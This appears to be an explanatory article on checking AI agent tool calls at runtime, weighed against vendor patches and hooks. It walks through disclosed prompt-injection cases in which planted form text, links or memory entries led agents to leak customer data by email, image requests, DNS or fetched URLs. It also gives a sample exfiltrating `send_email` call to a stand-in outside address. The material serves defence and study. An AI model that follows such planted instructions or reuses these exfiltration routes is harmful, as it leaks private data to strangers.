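# Runtime enforcement of AI agent tool calls, compared with patching and vendor security hooks

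## How an AI agent calls tools and where a defender can intervene

Runtime enforcement of AI agent tool calls uses software to check each action an AI agent proposes, just before the action runs, and can stop it. An AI agent here means a language model connected to programs that do things such as send email, run shell commands or change customer records. Defenders can also use patches and vendor hooks. A patch changes software or its default settings to remove a known flaw. A vendor hook is a point in a vendor's agent product where the customer's own check can run. (A webhook is a hook that sends a web request to an outside service and waits for the answer.) The three are not quite comparable, because a hook is a place to put a check rather than a check itself.

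### One tool call from start to finish

A language model by itself only produces text. To let it act, a developer describes a set of functions to it and writes ordinary software, the orchestrator, that receives the model's requests and carries them out. Each request is a tool call, a structured message that names one function and gives its arguments. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, part of the documentation for the Claude models, describes this arrangement as a contract in which the developer specifies the available operations and the format of their inputs, the model requests one, and the developer's code, never the model itself, runs it.

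The orchestrator runs in a loop. It sends the model the list of tools and the user's message, and the model responds with one or more tool calls and stops. The orchestrator runs each function, then sends the whole conversation back to the model in a new request, with the results added at the end. It repeats this until the model responds without a tool call. The model's context consists of the developer's instructions, the user's message and the results of earlier calls, and the model bases its next call only on that context.

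A defender can intervene after the model has written a call and before the orchestrator runs it, when the call is only data and has had no effect. Software can hold the call there until a check returns a decision, and the place where it does so is the enforcement point. Because the call has a fixed form, a check can read an email's recipient directly from its field. According to an opinion piece from the technology publisher O'Reilly, the whole approach depends on this fixed form, because if agents expressed their actions in prose, only another language model could interpret it, and that model would have the same weaknesses.

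The customer cannot always intervene in this gap. Anthropic runs some tools, including web search and code execution, on its own servers. These tools have usually run and returned their results by the time the customer's application receives the response, so the application can see what ran but could not hold the call beforehand.

Many tools come from yet another party, and the Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting agents to them. The agent application contains a client, which requests a list of tools from a tool server. The server returns each tool's name, a description and a schema for its inputs. When the model selects a tool, the client sends the tool's name and arguments to the server and passes the result back to the model. The model cannot contact the server directly, so the client is a natural place to check calls, but MCP does not supply the check. Model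 Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the relevant page of the specification, recommends that a person always be able to deny a call, but leaves open whether and how an application provides this. It requires clients to treat the labels that describe a tool's behaviour as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, so a check cannot rely on an untrusted server's label as evidence that a tool is harmless.

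The protocol also keeps no record of earlier calls. Model Context Protocol (2026) removed sessions in the version of 28 July 2026, and each request now stands alone and includes the client's identity. This makes servers easier to run, but a check that sees only incoming requests cannot tell from the protocol that an outgoing email came right after a read of the customer database. Detecting that sequence requires a separate record of earlier calls.

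### A sales agent and a public web form

For example, a small sales agent might have two tools: `read_leads`, which returns submissions from the company's web form, and `send_email`, which sends messages from the company's account. Anyone can use the form to leave a name, contact details and a question. Sales staff ask the agent to summarise new enquiries and reply to them, so `send_email` has to accept addresses outside the company. Someone then types into the question box an instruction to email the whole lead list to an outside address.

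1. An employee asks the agent for a summary of the leads. The model proposes `read_leads`, and the orchestrator runs it.
2. The result enters the context: the lead list, with the planted instruction sitting in one of its entries.
3. The model, working from a context that now includes the instruction, proposes a second call, to `send_email`.
4. The orchestrator runs the call, and the lead list leaves the company.
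5. A confirmation returns to the context, and the model writes the summary that the employee asked for.

The harmful call looks something like this:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "someone@outside.example",
    "subject": "Leads",
    "body": "(the lead list)"
  }
}
```

The tool call is well formed. The function exists, the arguments fit the schema, and the agent sends mail to outside addresses every day. The example is simplified, but O'Reilly recounts that in September 2025 researchers at Noma disclosed a similar attack on Salesforce's Agentforce, planted through a web-to-lead form.

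This kind of attack is called indirect prompt injection. The attacker hides instructions in content that an agent reads, and the model follows them. The attacker never talks to the agent and needs no account on any of the company's systems. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, gives the example of a job applicant who hides text in a CV telling the screening model to approve the application.

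David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, compares prompt injection with SQL injection to explain why it is hard to fix in the usual way. In SQL injection, an attacker types database commands into a web field and the database executes them. Programmers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which mark the user's input as data so that the database engine never treats it as a command. A language model has no equivalent marking to enforce. It predicts the next token (roughly, the next piece of a word) from all the text so far, which includes both the developer's instructions and the stranger's form entry. Developers can make attacks harder by training a model to give less weight to instructions in retrieved content, or by labelling that content as data. David C thinks such measures try to add a distinction that the underlying technology does not make, and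 that prompt injection may well never have a complete fix. That is a judgement about how current models work, not a proof, but a defender who accepts even part of it has to plan for the model proposing a bad call.

### The confused deputy

Permissions did nothing here because the agent was allowed both to read the leads and to send email. Researchers at Microsoft observe more generally that an attacker who can influence a business agent's plan can cause harmful behaviour that stays within the agent's permissions, which makes it hard for traditional controls to detect.

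Computer security calls a program in this position a confused deputy, meaning that it has authority of its own and somebody without that authority gets the program to use it for them. The term comes from *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988), which describes a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler had permission to write files in its own directory because it kept usage statistics there. The company's billing file was in the same directory. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file. The operating system checked that the compiler could write there and let it overwrite the billing records.

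Hardy traced the problem to the compiler having two sources of authority, the user who started it and its own licence to write in that directory. The compiler had no way to specify which one to use for a given file. His remedy was the capability, a token that both identifies a file and authorises writing to it. The compiler would then write the debugging output using only the capabilities the user had given it, and the user had none for the billing file.

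The sales agent fits the pattern closely, because it uses the company's authority to send email that a stranger suggested. The remedy carries over less well. In a compiler, separate pieces of code write the statistics and the debugging output, so a programmer can attach the right authority to each. In the agent, one model produces every call from one undivided context. David C says engineers can repair a classical confused deputy, but he calls a language model "inherently confusable" and advises them to use ordinary, non-AI safeguards to limit what the system can do.

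Such a safeguard needs more information than the function's name. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes a seven-event case much like the sales example. The user asks for a summary of an outside vendor's document, the agent reads the document with its injected instruction, then reads a sensitive internal file, and finally tries to email an external recipient. The paper points out that the email is harmless if its content depends only on public information, but dangerous if it depends on both the untrusted document and the sensitive file. The call to `send_email` can have the same form in both cases, but its provenance, the record of which inputs influenced it, differs.

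### Where a patch, a runtime check and a vendor hook act

A patch acts earliest, before the employee types anything. If the company's engineers notice that `read_leads` returns every record ever submitted when the task needs only this week's, they can fix it once, and each later run will expose fewer records without delaying the call. They cannot patch the model's tendency to follow instructions it finds in a form entry, because no particular line of code causes it.

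A runtime check acts after the model proposes `send_email` and before the orchestrator executes it. A check on the earlier `read_leads` call would have found little wrong, because the employee had asked for the leads and the planted instruction had not yet entered the context. The `send_email` call is the first with visible signs of trouble, an outside recipient and a body full of other people's contact details. How the check responds depends on its policy, the rules for which calls to allow, block or send to a person for approval.

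A vendor hook runs a check at that same point in the sequence, but inside software the vendor owns. A company that wrote its own orchestrator can add a check to the loop directly, while one that bought its agent can add a check there only where the vendor allows it. In Copilot Studio, Microsoft's product for building agents, the orchestrator sends a description of each planned action to a security service, which allows or blocks the action before it runs.

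The hook protects nothing by itself. If the sales company attaches a script that logs and approves every call, the lead list is still stolen, though the log records the theft. A different script on the same hook could hold any external email that contains more than one person's contact details until a member of staff has reviewed it. That would stop the theft and let ordinary replies to enquirers through. Protection also depends on what the vendor's software does when the check crashes or takes too long. It may let the call run, which engineers call failing open, or block it, which they call failing closed.

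### A yardstick from 1972

The standard test for an enforcement point comes from *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), which reports the findings of a panel working for the US Air Force. The panel studied how people with different security clearances could share one computer when any of them might write a hostile program and run it with legitimate access. It had little faith in repairing systems flaw by flaw. "Tiger teams" of friendly attackers had broken into every system they were known to have tried, and fixing the flaws they found gave no assurance that they had found them all.

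What the panel recommended was a reference monitor, an idea that Anderson credits to earlier work by Lampson and by Graham and Denning. A reference monitor checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the user behind it may do. It has to meet three requirements:

- It is always invoked: every attempt goes through the check, because any program that can skip it becomes part of the security machinery and needs just as much trust.
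- Nobody can tamper with it: if a program under the monitor's control can alter the monitor, its verdicts are worth nothing.
- It is small enough to verify: people must be able to analyse and test it completely, or they have no grounds for believing that it works in every case.

These requirements are hard to meet, as Anderson showed by applying them to GCOS III, the operating system of a Honeywell computer. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, which is a reference monitor of a sort. But most parts of the operating system ran without that confinement when acting on the program's behalf, so the check was not always invoked. If the operating system itself is counted as the monitor, then the monitor had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify. Similarly, if an agent's email tool passes through a check but its shell commands do not, the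 check is not always invoked.

The three requirements, however, apply to the mechanism and not to the rules it enforces. Anderson pictured the list of permissions as a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each thing they might use, and the permitted operations in the cells. The sales agent's row would have "allowed" under both `read_leads` and `send_email`, so even a flawless reference monitor would let the agent email out the lead list. Hardy recognized this and left it as an exercise for his readers to show that lists of permissions do not solve the confused deputy problem. Palumbo and colleagues, who built a reference monitor for agents, limit their own guarantee in the same way. It covers only what the policy forbids, and it holds only if the monitor intercepts every relevant action and receives accurate information about what led up to it.

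## What patching fixes and what it leaves open

Patching starts when somebody finds a flaw, and with AI agents that has often been an outside security researcher. The researcher privately tells the vendor, who confirms the flaw, writes a fix and gets it into the software customers use. Both normally wait until then to publish the details, because a detailed report helps attackers as well as defenders. Until the fix arrives, customers unknowingly run flawed software, and anyone else who finds the flaw can exploit it.

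How the fix reaches customers depends on who runs the software. Vendors host many business agents on their own servers, so one update reaches every customer. For a coding agent on a developer's laptop or an MCP server on a company's own machine, the vendor can only publish a new version, and each copy stays vulnerable until its owner installs it. Meanwhile, attackers can compare the two versions to find the flaw in the old one. The flaws that researchers reported in Microsoft's Copilot products and Salesforce's Agentforce in 2025 and 2026 were in hosted services, which are easier to patch.

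### ShareLeak from discovery to disclosure

In April 2026 the startup Capsule Security (2026) announced ShareLeak, a flaw in Copilot Studio that closely resembles the sales agent's web form flaw. A stranger could type instructions into the comment field of a public form in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for sharing files and lists within a company, and the agent that processed the form would follow them. In Capsule's test, the agent looked up customer records in SharePoint and emailed them to an outside address through Outlook.

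The dates of discovery, confirmation and repair come from a VentureBeat article, reposted on diyhaven858.wasmer.app as *Microsoft patched a Copilot Studio prompt injection. The data exfiltrated anyway* (2026). Two more dates come from MITRE's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the flaw's entry in CVE, the public catalogue of known software vulnerabilities.

- 24 November 2025: Capsule finds the flaw.
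- 5 December: Microsoft confirms it.
- 30 December: Microsoft reserves the number CVE-2026-21520.
- 15 January 2026: Microsoft deploys the fix.
- 22 January: Microsoft publishes the CVE entry, with a one-sentence description.
- 15 April: Capsule publishes its research.

Microsoft took 11 days to confirm the flaw and another 41 to fix it, leaving it open for 52 days after its discovery. Capsule then waited 90 days before explaining the flaw publicly.

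The exposure lasted longer than 52 days, because the flaw existed before Capsule looked for it. VentureBeat advised companies to search their logs from 24 November to 15 January for signs of an attack. A company with an older agent would do better to search back to the day the agent first read a public form. The CVE entry does not help narrow the period, because its version field contains only a dash.

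Customers of a hosted service have no update to install. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) notes that Microsoft made the change internally and that users had nothing to do. This avoids the usual problem of customers who never update, but it also means customers have to trust that the fix works. The CVE entry records an official fix without describing what Microsoft changed.

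### Did data leak after the patch?

Some coverage gave the impression that the fix had failed. VentureBeat reported in its headline that Microsoft had patched the flaw and "the data exfiltrated anyway" (exfiltration is the unauthorised transfer of data to an outside party). Claw Times, which relayed the story, went further and described a patch that did not hold.

The body of VentureBeat's article supports a narrower claim. During Capsule's testing, Microsoft's safety mechanisms flagged the request as suspicious, but the data left anyway. The "anyway" therefore means despite the warning, not despite the patch. The article doesn't date the test, but nothing in it indicates that the test took place after 15 January. CSO Online also reports that the researchers found the leak and that Microsoft patched the flaw after they disclosed it.

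Capsule Security's press release also describes ShareLeak as patched and mentions no leak after the fix. The company had a strong motive to mention one, since it was launching a product that checks agents' actions at runtime, and a failed patch would have helped sell it. Claw Times offers no evidence of its own, and it calls the patch four months old when its own dates make it three. The story of a leak after the patch therefore seems to come from a misread headline. However, neither Capsule's release nor the CVE entry reports a retest, so it is still unclear how complete the fix was.

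Criminals are not known to have used the flaw. STAR Labs' *Copilot Studio* (2026), which reproduces the fields of Microsoft's advisory, lists it as not exploited. The US cybersecurity agency CISA also listed no exploitation when it assessed the flaw on 24 January. The title of OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks* (2026), an entry in a monitor of AI incidents, suggests real victims, but the entry's AI-generated summary describes vulnerabilities that Capsule discovered.

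### A defect in the code and a tendency in the model

ShareLeak had two causes, only one of which was an ordinary defect. In Capsule's testing, Copilot Studio joined the form's text directly to the agent's instructions without cleaning it first, so a stranger's comment could pass for a system message. Programmers can fix that by keeping form text in a separate, labelled place and removing anything that imitates a system message.

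The other cause was the model's tendency to follow instructions wherever it finds them, which David C thinks may never have a complete fix. An agent whose job is to process form submissions has to read them, so a stranger's words still reach the model after the patch.

The CVE entry obscures this difference because Microsoft classified ShareLeak as command injection, in the same broad family as SQL injection. Most flaws in that family can be fixed completely, since a reviewer can read the corrected code and conclude that no input will ever run as a command. Nobody can yet read a language model that way, so a vendor can instead report that a known attack has stopped working. Microsoft makes this kind of claim about prompt injection in Copilot. It says it keeps deploying mitigations and that, in multiple cases, people could no longer reproduce behaviour they had reported earlier.

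After a patch blocks one prompt injection, an attacker can try different wording. CX Today's *A Customer Service AI Agent Spits Out Complete Salesforce Records* recounts an earlier attack on Copilot Studio, which the security firm Zenity presented at DEF CON in 2025. Zenity built a copy of an agent used by the consultancy McKinsey, connected it to a test Salesforce account and got it to hand over complete customer records. Microsoft confirmed that the injection no longer works, but Zenity warned that more than 3,500 public-facing agents remained open to similar ones. I would not rely on that figure, because it is Zenity's own and the firm sells protection for agents, but the risk from reworded attacks does not depend on it.

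Vendors also differ on whether a weakness like this should get a CVE. Capsule called Microsoft's decision to assign one to an agent-building platform "highly unusual". Microsoft had earlier assigned one to EchoLeak, a prompt injection flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that it patched in June 2025. EchoLeak scored 9.3 out of 10 on the CVSS severity scale, and ShareLeak scored 7.5. Salesforce had not assigned a CVE to a parallel flaw in Agentforce when Capsule published it, so a security team that relied on the CVE catalogue would have missed it.

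### Agentforce and its three exits

That parallel flaw followed ForcedLeak, Noma's web-form attack on Agentforce. The Hacker News (2025) lists ForcedLeak's severity as 9.4. The attack sent data out through an image. To display an image, a browser requests it from a server, and the address in that request can carry data to whoever runs the server.

Salesforce had a safeguard against this, a content security policy, which lists the domains a page may load content from. One domain on the list had expired. As the software developer Simon Willison recounts, the researchers registered it and watched lead data arrive in their server's logs. Salesforce corrected the list, then added a control called Trusted URLs, which stops its agents from generating links to unapproved domains. According to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*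 (2025), Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, Salesforce acknowledged it on 31 July and began enforcing Trusted URLs on 8 September, 42 days after the report, and the details became public on 25 September.

Both changes affected where the data could go but not how the agent read a lead. Varonis, a data security company, observed that Trusted URLs blocked untrusted domains but that structural fixes to how agents process context "remain elusive".

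Capsule then reported PipeLeak, an attack that again put instructions into a public lead form, but this time the agent emailed the leads out. Trusted URLs did not help, because the email went through a tool the agent had permission to use. A rule about outside recipients might have caught it. One form entry was enough to extract many records. Capsule's chief executive, Naor Paz, told VentureBeat that the test never reached a limit, and the employee who had started the agent saw no sign that any data had left.

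Salesforce at first disputed part of this. According to CSO Online, it acknowledged the prompt injection but called the exfiltration route "configuration-specific", since customers could turn on a setting that asks a person to confirm the agent's actions. Capsule objected that the default was insecure and that constant approval defeats the purpose of an agent. According to Claw Times, a Salesforce spokesperson said after VentureBeat's article appeared that the company had "remediated the specific scenario described" and that confirmation was now on by default for email actions. CISO Whisperer's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* counts both ShareLeak and PipeLeak as addressed.

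Changing a default setting is also a useful patch because it protects customers who never open the settings page. But fixing one specific scenario doesn't guarantee protection against the next, and in this case another soon followed. Poireault (2026), in *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*, reports that Zenity found a way past Trusted URLs itself, which let customer data leave through DNS, the system computers use to look up the address behind a domain name. Zenity reported these weaknesses, known as SalesBleed, in June 2026, and Salesforce fixed them on 18 August.

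In about a year, three research teams injected instructions into Agentforce and got data out by three different routes. Salesforce responded to each report, and each response made the product safer. But an agent with access to customer records was still taking instructions from strangers. The fixes closed routes one at a time, which works only if someone can list them all.

### Leaks that do not pass through a tool call

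Elia Zaitsev, chief technology officer of the security company CrowdStrike, told VentureBeat that patching every vulnerability is impossible and that people forget about runtime security. CrowdStrike sells runtime security, so he has an interest in saying this, but the history of Agentforce gives his claim some support. However, some leaks don't happen through a tool call that a runtime check could intercept.

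Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes such a leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise, which searches a company's mail, calendars and files. The victim had to click one link, and the link led to a real Microsoft address. The attack then depended on three weaknesses:

- Copilot treated the search text in the link as instructions to follow.
- Microsoft's software made images in Copilot's answer harmless only once the answer was complete, while the browser displayed the answer as it arrived and had already sent the request for the image.
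- The content security policy allowed requests to Bing, Microsoft's search engine, and Bing's own servers would then contact an outside address.

Copilot only searched the user's mail and wrote an answer. The user was allowed to run that search, and it is what the product is for. The data left afterwards, in the browser's request for an image. A check on outgoing tool calls would look for something like an email or an upload, so it might have missed this request. It might have stopped the search, but only if it could detect that the instructions came from a link and not from the user.

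Patching suits this sort of flaw well. Varonis points out that the attack needed all three weaknesses, so fixing any one of them would have stopped it, and the second and third are familiar kinds of web bug. Microsoft fixed SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824) before Varonis published the details on 15 June 2026. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* places the fix earlier that month and urges readers to "patch now", but Microsoft had made the repair on its side, and SC Media's *SearchLeak vulnerability allows data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise* confirms that users did not need to act.

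Another Microsoft product, Copilot Cowork, had a problem that falls somewhere in between. Willison (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, explains that the agent could send email to the user's own inbox without asking for approval. A check that only compared the recipient with a list of outsiders would let these messages through. But they could contain images from outside servers, and when the user opened a message, the request for the image could carry data out, including download links that open the user's files without a further login. A runtime check would run on the tool call, but the leak happened later, when the message was displayed. The vendor can deal with that by changing how it displays messages from the agent. A runtime check would have to scan the body of each message and flag the image as a risk.

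### CoSnitch and the length of exposure

All of this assumes the fix arrives reasonably soon. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes a flaw in Copilot Personal, Microsoft's consumer assistant, that Varonis reported in December 2025 and Microsoft fixed about eight months later, on 18 August 2026. Varonis gives no reason for the delay.

As with SearchLeak, one click on a link was enough to make Copilot follow an attacker's instructions. Copilot could then collect data from services the user had connected to it, such as Gmail, and send the data out in the address of a web page it fetched. Fetching pages is one of Copilot's built-in abilities, so in CoSnitch the data did leave through an action of the agent. A check before the fetch could have examined the address. But Copilot fetches pages inside Microsoft's service, so consumers would have had to wait for Microsoft to add such a check, just as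 they waited for the patch.

Varonis had found the same kind of opening in Reprompt, another flaw in Copilot Personal. Windows Central (2026) reports that Varonis told Microsoft about Reprompt in August 2025 and that Microsoft had patched it by 13 January 2026. Varonis was then surprised to find that the technique also worked in the Enterprise product, where it expected stronger guardrails. It published this second flaw, SearchLeak, in June, while CoSnitch was still unpatched. For two months, attackers could read in detail how a link could be used to attack Enterprise users while a similar weakness remained in Copilot Personal.

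CoSnitch also involved damage that a patch does not automatically reverse. Copilot keeps a memory of each user that lasts across conversations. Varonis showed that a web page could plant instructions in this memory when the user asked Copilot to summarise the page. The instructions survived a password change and stayed until the user deleted them. A patch can therefore block new instructions while leaving old ones in place, and UNU notes that most users never review their memory settings.

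The known dates give the following intervals. Where a source gives only the month of the report, the interval is a range.

| Flaw | Product | Reported | Fixed | Days open after report | Source |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ForcedLeak | Agentforce | 28 July 2025 | 8 September 2025 | 42 | ThaiCERT |
| Reprompt | Copilot Personal | August 2025 | 13 January 2026 | 135–165 | Windows Central |
| ShareLeak | Copilot Studio | 24 November 2025 | 15 January 2026 | 52 | Claw Times |
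| SalesBleed | Agentforce | June 2026 | 18 August 2026 | 49–78 | Poireault |
| CoSnitch | Copilot Personal | December 2025 | 18 August 2026 | 230–260 | Varonis |

Five flaws are too few for a meaningful average, and all five are ones that researchers chose to publicise. The quickest fix still took six weeks, even though these companies run the software themselves and do not have to wait for customers to install an update.

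The cases give no figure for the time from disclosure to exploitation, because nobody has reported exploitation of ShareLeak, SearchLeak or CoSnitch. Microsoft's advisory and CISA report none for ShareLeak, ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* (2026) found no reports of attacks using SearchLeak, and Varonis saw no evidence of attacks using CoSnitch. This is only mildly reassuring, since these attacks are hard to notice. Varonis says that a planted memory leaves no log entry that security tools would flag. STAR Labs also lists a score of about 1.4% for ShareLeak from EPSS, a system that estimates the chance that attackers will exploit a flaw in the next 30 days. The score means little here, because Microsoft has already removed the flaw from its only copy of the service.

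When customers have to install a fix themselves, a flaw can become public before they are protected. Suppose that the developer of an MCP server took 52 days to fix a flaw, as Microsoft did with ShareLeak, and that a company took another 30 days to install the new version. The company would be exposed for 82 days after the discovery, and the flaw could be public knowledge for the last 30. The 30 days are invented for the example, because customers of hosted services install nothing and so provide no real figure. Until the company installed the new version, a runtime check could protect it, provided that the attack ended in a tool call and the check had a rule that recognised it.

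## Checking a tool call against fixed rules

The simplest runtime check is ordinary code that applies prewritten rules to a proposed tool call. It always returns the same answer for the same facts. Because no language model is involved in the decision, an instruction planted in a web form cannot override the rules. The check's effectiveness depends on how well the rules fit the agent's work and which facts the code can access.

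### From a proposed call to a decision

*Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes the decision on a tool call as a function with four inputs and three possible results. Agentao is open-source software for running agents on a user's own machine.

```
D(tool, arguments, state, policy) → allow, prompt or deny
```

"Prompt" here means asking a person. The state is what the software has recorded about the run so far, such as earlier calls and any limits the user has set.

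A rule in Agentao consists of a result and three tests, one each for the tool's name, its arguments and the state. The rule applies only if the call meets all three. For the sales agent, a rule might cover calls to `send_email` with a recipient outside the company in a run that has already read more than one lead. Its result might be to ask a member of staff.

The check then takes five steps:

1. Interception: the call waits at the enforcement point. FORGE, the monitor that Palumbo and colleagues built, wraps the functions through which an agent framework sends its calls, and holds each call there until it has a verdict.
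2. Argument parsing: the software decodes the arguments and looks up the tool. If the call is malformed or names an unknown tool, Agentao sends the model an error.
3. Rule evaluation: the code collects the facts the rules need and tests the rules against them. FORGE first waits for its record of the run to catch up. Otherwise an email might go out before the monitor had registered the file read that made it dangerous.
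4. Decision: the tool runs, a person gets a question, or the model gets an error message and can propose something else.
5. Logging: Agentao records a decision for every attempted call, and a start and an end for every call that runs, so staff can later work out what happened.

Rules can contradict each other. Agentao checks them in a fixed order: built-in bans, restrictions for the current run, the host application's own rules, and finally the defaults for the mode the user chose. Among the host's rules, the first match decides, so a broad permission placed above a narrow ban overrides it. In FORGE, a denial overrides any permission, wherever it appears in the list. When no rule matches, FORGE leaves the default to whoever deploys it. Agentao runs the call unless the tool is marked as needing confirmation, so a tool that a company adds without a rule may run automatically.

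### Three rules for the sales agent

Here are three rules that would each stop the theft of the sales agent's lead list:

```
Argument rule:    deny send_email if the recipient's domain is not on the list
History rule:     deny outside email if this run has read more than one lead
Provenance rule:  deny outside email unless the recipient is the contact
                  address of the lead the agent is answering
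```

The argument rule needs only the `to` field and a list of permitted domains. Since `outside.example` is not on the list, the rule blocks the email containing the stolen leads. But the agent's job is to write to strangers, and the rule also blocks the first reply to any customer whose domain nobody has added. The company could list the public mail providers that many enquirers use, but the thief can open an account there too. A domain list suits an agent that writes only to colleagues and known suppliers.

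The history rule blocks `send_email` whatever the address or content, because the run has already read the whole lead list by the time the model proposes the email. It also blocks every legitimate reply that follows a summary of new enquiries, which is what the staff asked for. The rule needs a log of the run's calls and the number of records each one returned, which MCP does not keep. The company could keep the rule by splitting the work. One run would read the list and write the summary, then a fresh run for each enquiry would open a single record and reply. This would be practical only after `read_leads` is changed so that it can return one lead.

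The provenance rule lets the agent answer strangers. An address that appears only in the question box fails because it did not come from the contact field. The rule also blocks some harmless email, such as when an enquirer uses the question box to ask for a copy to a colleague, or when an employee tells the agent to forward a lead to a partner firm. The company could fix the second case by also accepting addresses the employee typed. The software has to know which lead the agent is handling and keep each value attached to the field it came from. If `read_leads` returned the leads as one block of text, it would be hard to tell which field an address came from.

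The provenance rule, however, accepts any address in the contact field, and strangers fill in that field, so a thief who entered his own address would count as a legitimate recipient. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, acknowledge the same weakness in a checking system they built at the company Corners. One of their rules lets a banking agent pay anyone in the account's transaction history, so an attacker who first sent the account a small payment might become a known payee. For the sales agent, a further rule could bar emails from containing any contact details except the recipient's. This would stop the agent from pasting in the lead list, but a paraphrase of other people's enquiries would be harder to detect.

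### What a monitor can enforce

A check of this kind can't enforce some requirements, however carefully someone writes the rules. Fred Schneider's standard result from 2000 shows that a monitor that watches a program run and can only halt it can enforce only safety properties. A safety property forbids something, and every breach happens at a definite point in the run. The events up to that point establish the breach, and nothing later can undo it. "No outside email after a bulk read" is a safety property because the breach happens when the email goes out, and the monitor can halt the program just before.

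A monitor cannot enforce the rule "every enquiry eventually gets a reply" by halting the agent. However long an enquiry has waited, the reply might still come, and halting the agent would not send it. Monitors for agents usually block a single call and let the run continue instead of halting it. The model may then propose a permitted call, but the monitor cannot make it do so.

Influence is harder to check. Determining whether the stranger's form entry changed an email would require comparing the actual run with one in which the entry was different, and the monitor can observe only the actual run. FORGE therefore takes a cautious approach and treats every message from a model as dependent on everything in the history the model received. This should miss no real influence as long as the record is complete. But once the sales agent has read the leads, everything it proposes counts as influenced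 by strangers, including honest replies. The provenance rule above avoids this problem because it only compares an address with a field, regardless of why the model chose that address.

A rule that each call must serve the user's purpose would stop nearly every injection. Schneider's result does not rule out such a rule, since a call that fails to serve the purpose breaks it at a definite moment. But the code has to judge this from the tool, the arguments and the recorded state, and none of them contains the purpose. The employee's request contains it, but often only in part. For example, "Reply to the new enquiries" does not specify what a reply may contain.

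Yu and colleagues tried to approximate a rule forbidding changes that the user had not requested. Their code treats a payment as requested if the user named the recipient or the recipient appears in the transaction history. It accepts any other change if the user's messages contain a verb such as "update" or "pay", or refer the agent to a document to act on. In one test, the user had asked for an email, and the check accepted an injected calendar entry because the user had requested *some* change. In another, it refused a user's request to "add an event" because the request contained none of the listed verbs. Judging the purpose of a call requires a model or a person.

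### Writing the rules

The direct way to turn a company's intentions into rules is to write code. In *Reason Less, Verify More*, Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026) wrote four short checks for the airline part of τ²-bench, a benchmark in which agents serve simulated customers under a written company policy. The checks block cancellations of ineligible bookings, changes to the number of passengers, incorrect baggage updates, and changes to records the agent has not read. The paper credits earlier systems such as AEGIS and AgentSpec with establishing the idea. The checks fail open, so if one crashes, the tool call still runs. This avoids needless blocks in a study of accidental mistakes, but it would be a poor choice against an attacker who might cause the crash.

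Palumbo and colleagues write rules in Datalog, a language designed for querying databases. FORGE stores each run as a graph in which messages, calls and results are nodes, and arrows lead from each event to the later events it may have influenced. To stop the email in their example, where an agent reads a hostile vendor document and then a sensitive file, they use a rule of this form:

```
Deny(a)    :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
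Tainted(e) :- UntrustedInput(e).
Tainted(e) :- DependsOn(e, e'), Tainted(e').
```

The top line denies an action if it sends something outside and depends on both untrusted content and sensitive data. The other lines define an event as tainted if it is untrusted input or depends on a tainted event. `HasSecret` has a matching definition. Because the definition refers to itself, it can follow a chain of any length, for example from a document to a summary to a second agent's message to an email. Palumbo and colleagues chose Datalog partly because evaluation always finishes and gives a single result, which matters when a call is waiting.

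Many companies already have their policies in prose, and several teams use a language model to translate them into rules. NOMOS uses the model only during preparation. Code splits the policy document into clauses, and the model makes five attempts at turning each clause into candidate rules, using a fixed list of conditions. Code then repairs or rejects candidates that could not work, and a majority vote removes those that appeared in too few of the five attempts. For instance, NOMOS turned the sentence "Basic economy flights cannot be modified" into a rule that bans the tool for updating flights whenever the booking is in basic economy.

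As Yu and colleagues describe it, VeriGuard turns a policy into program code and uses a verifier to prove that each function meets a formal contract. This guarantee is stronger than that of NOMOS. But each policy needs a contract, and a language model still converts the agent's data into the function's inputs at every check.

In *ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, 2026), a model drafts rules from tool descriptions, successful attacks and recordings of normal tasks. Some rules limit each task to the tools it needs, some apply to every task, and some require a further condition, such as approval, for doubtful calls. The rules refer to a limited set of facts, each with only a few possible values, so a program called a solver can search all combinations for one that the rules allow but a stated safety requirement forbids. If it finds one, the model revises the rules.

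The solver's proof covers only the stated requirements, and it holds only if the facts are correct. A language model supplies some of those facts while the agent runs, such as whether an argument came from an untrusted source. So although ActGov's last step follows fixed rules, it depends on a model's interpretation of possibly hostile text, and the model's mistakes carry over into the decision.

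Rules can also come from the user's own request. Progent, an older system, can have a model generate a policy for each task from that request. When Yu and colleagues reran it on simulated banking tasks, 16 attacks still succeeded. Nine of them were in a single task where the user asked the agent to pay a bill "like last month". The request didn't specify an account, so a policy based on it could not restrict the recipient, and the attacker's account number was allowed. A standing rule about known payees did not have this problem.

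### Errors in the rules

A monitor enforces a rule exactly as written, even if the rule is mistaken. Yu and colleagues counted the mistakes in the rules their model produced from τ²-bench's airline and retail policies. They found that 37% of the 79 candidate airline rules and 13% of the 53 candidate retail rules were unusable as they stood or needed repair. One rule, based on a clause about authenticating the customer first, blocked every tool until authentication, including the two tools that perform it, so no conversation could have got past that point. In a separate trial with the automatic checks turned off, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could never have worked.

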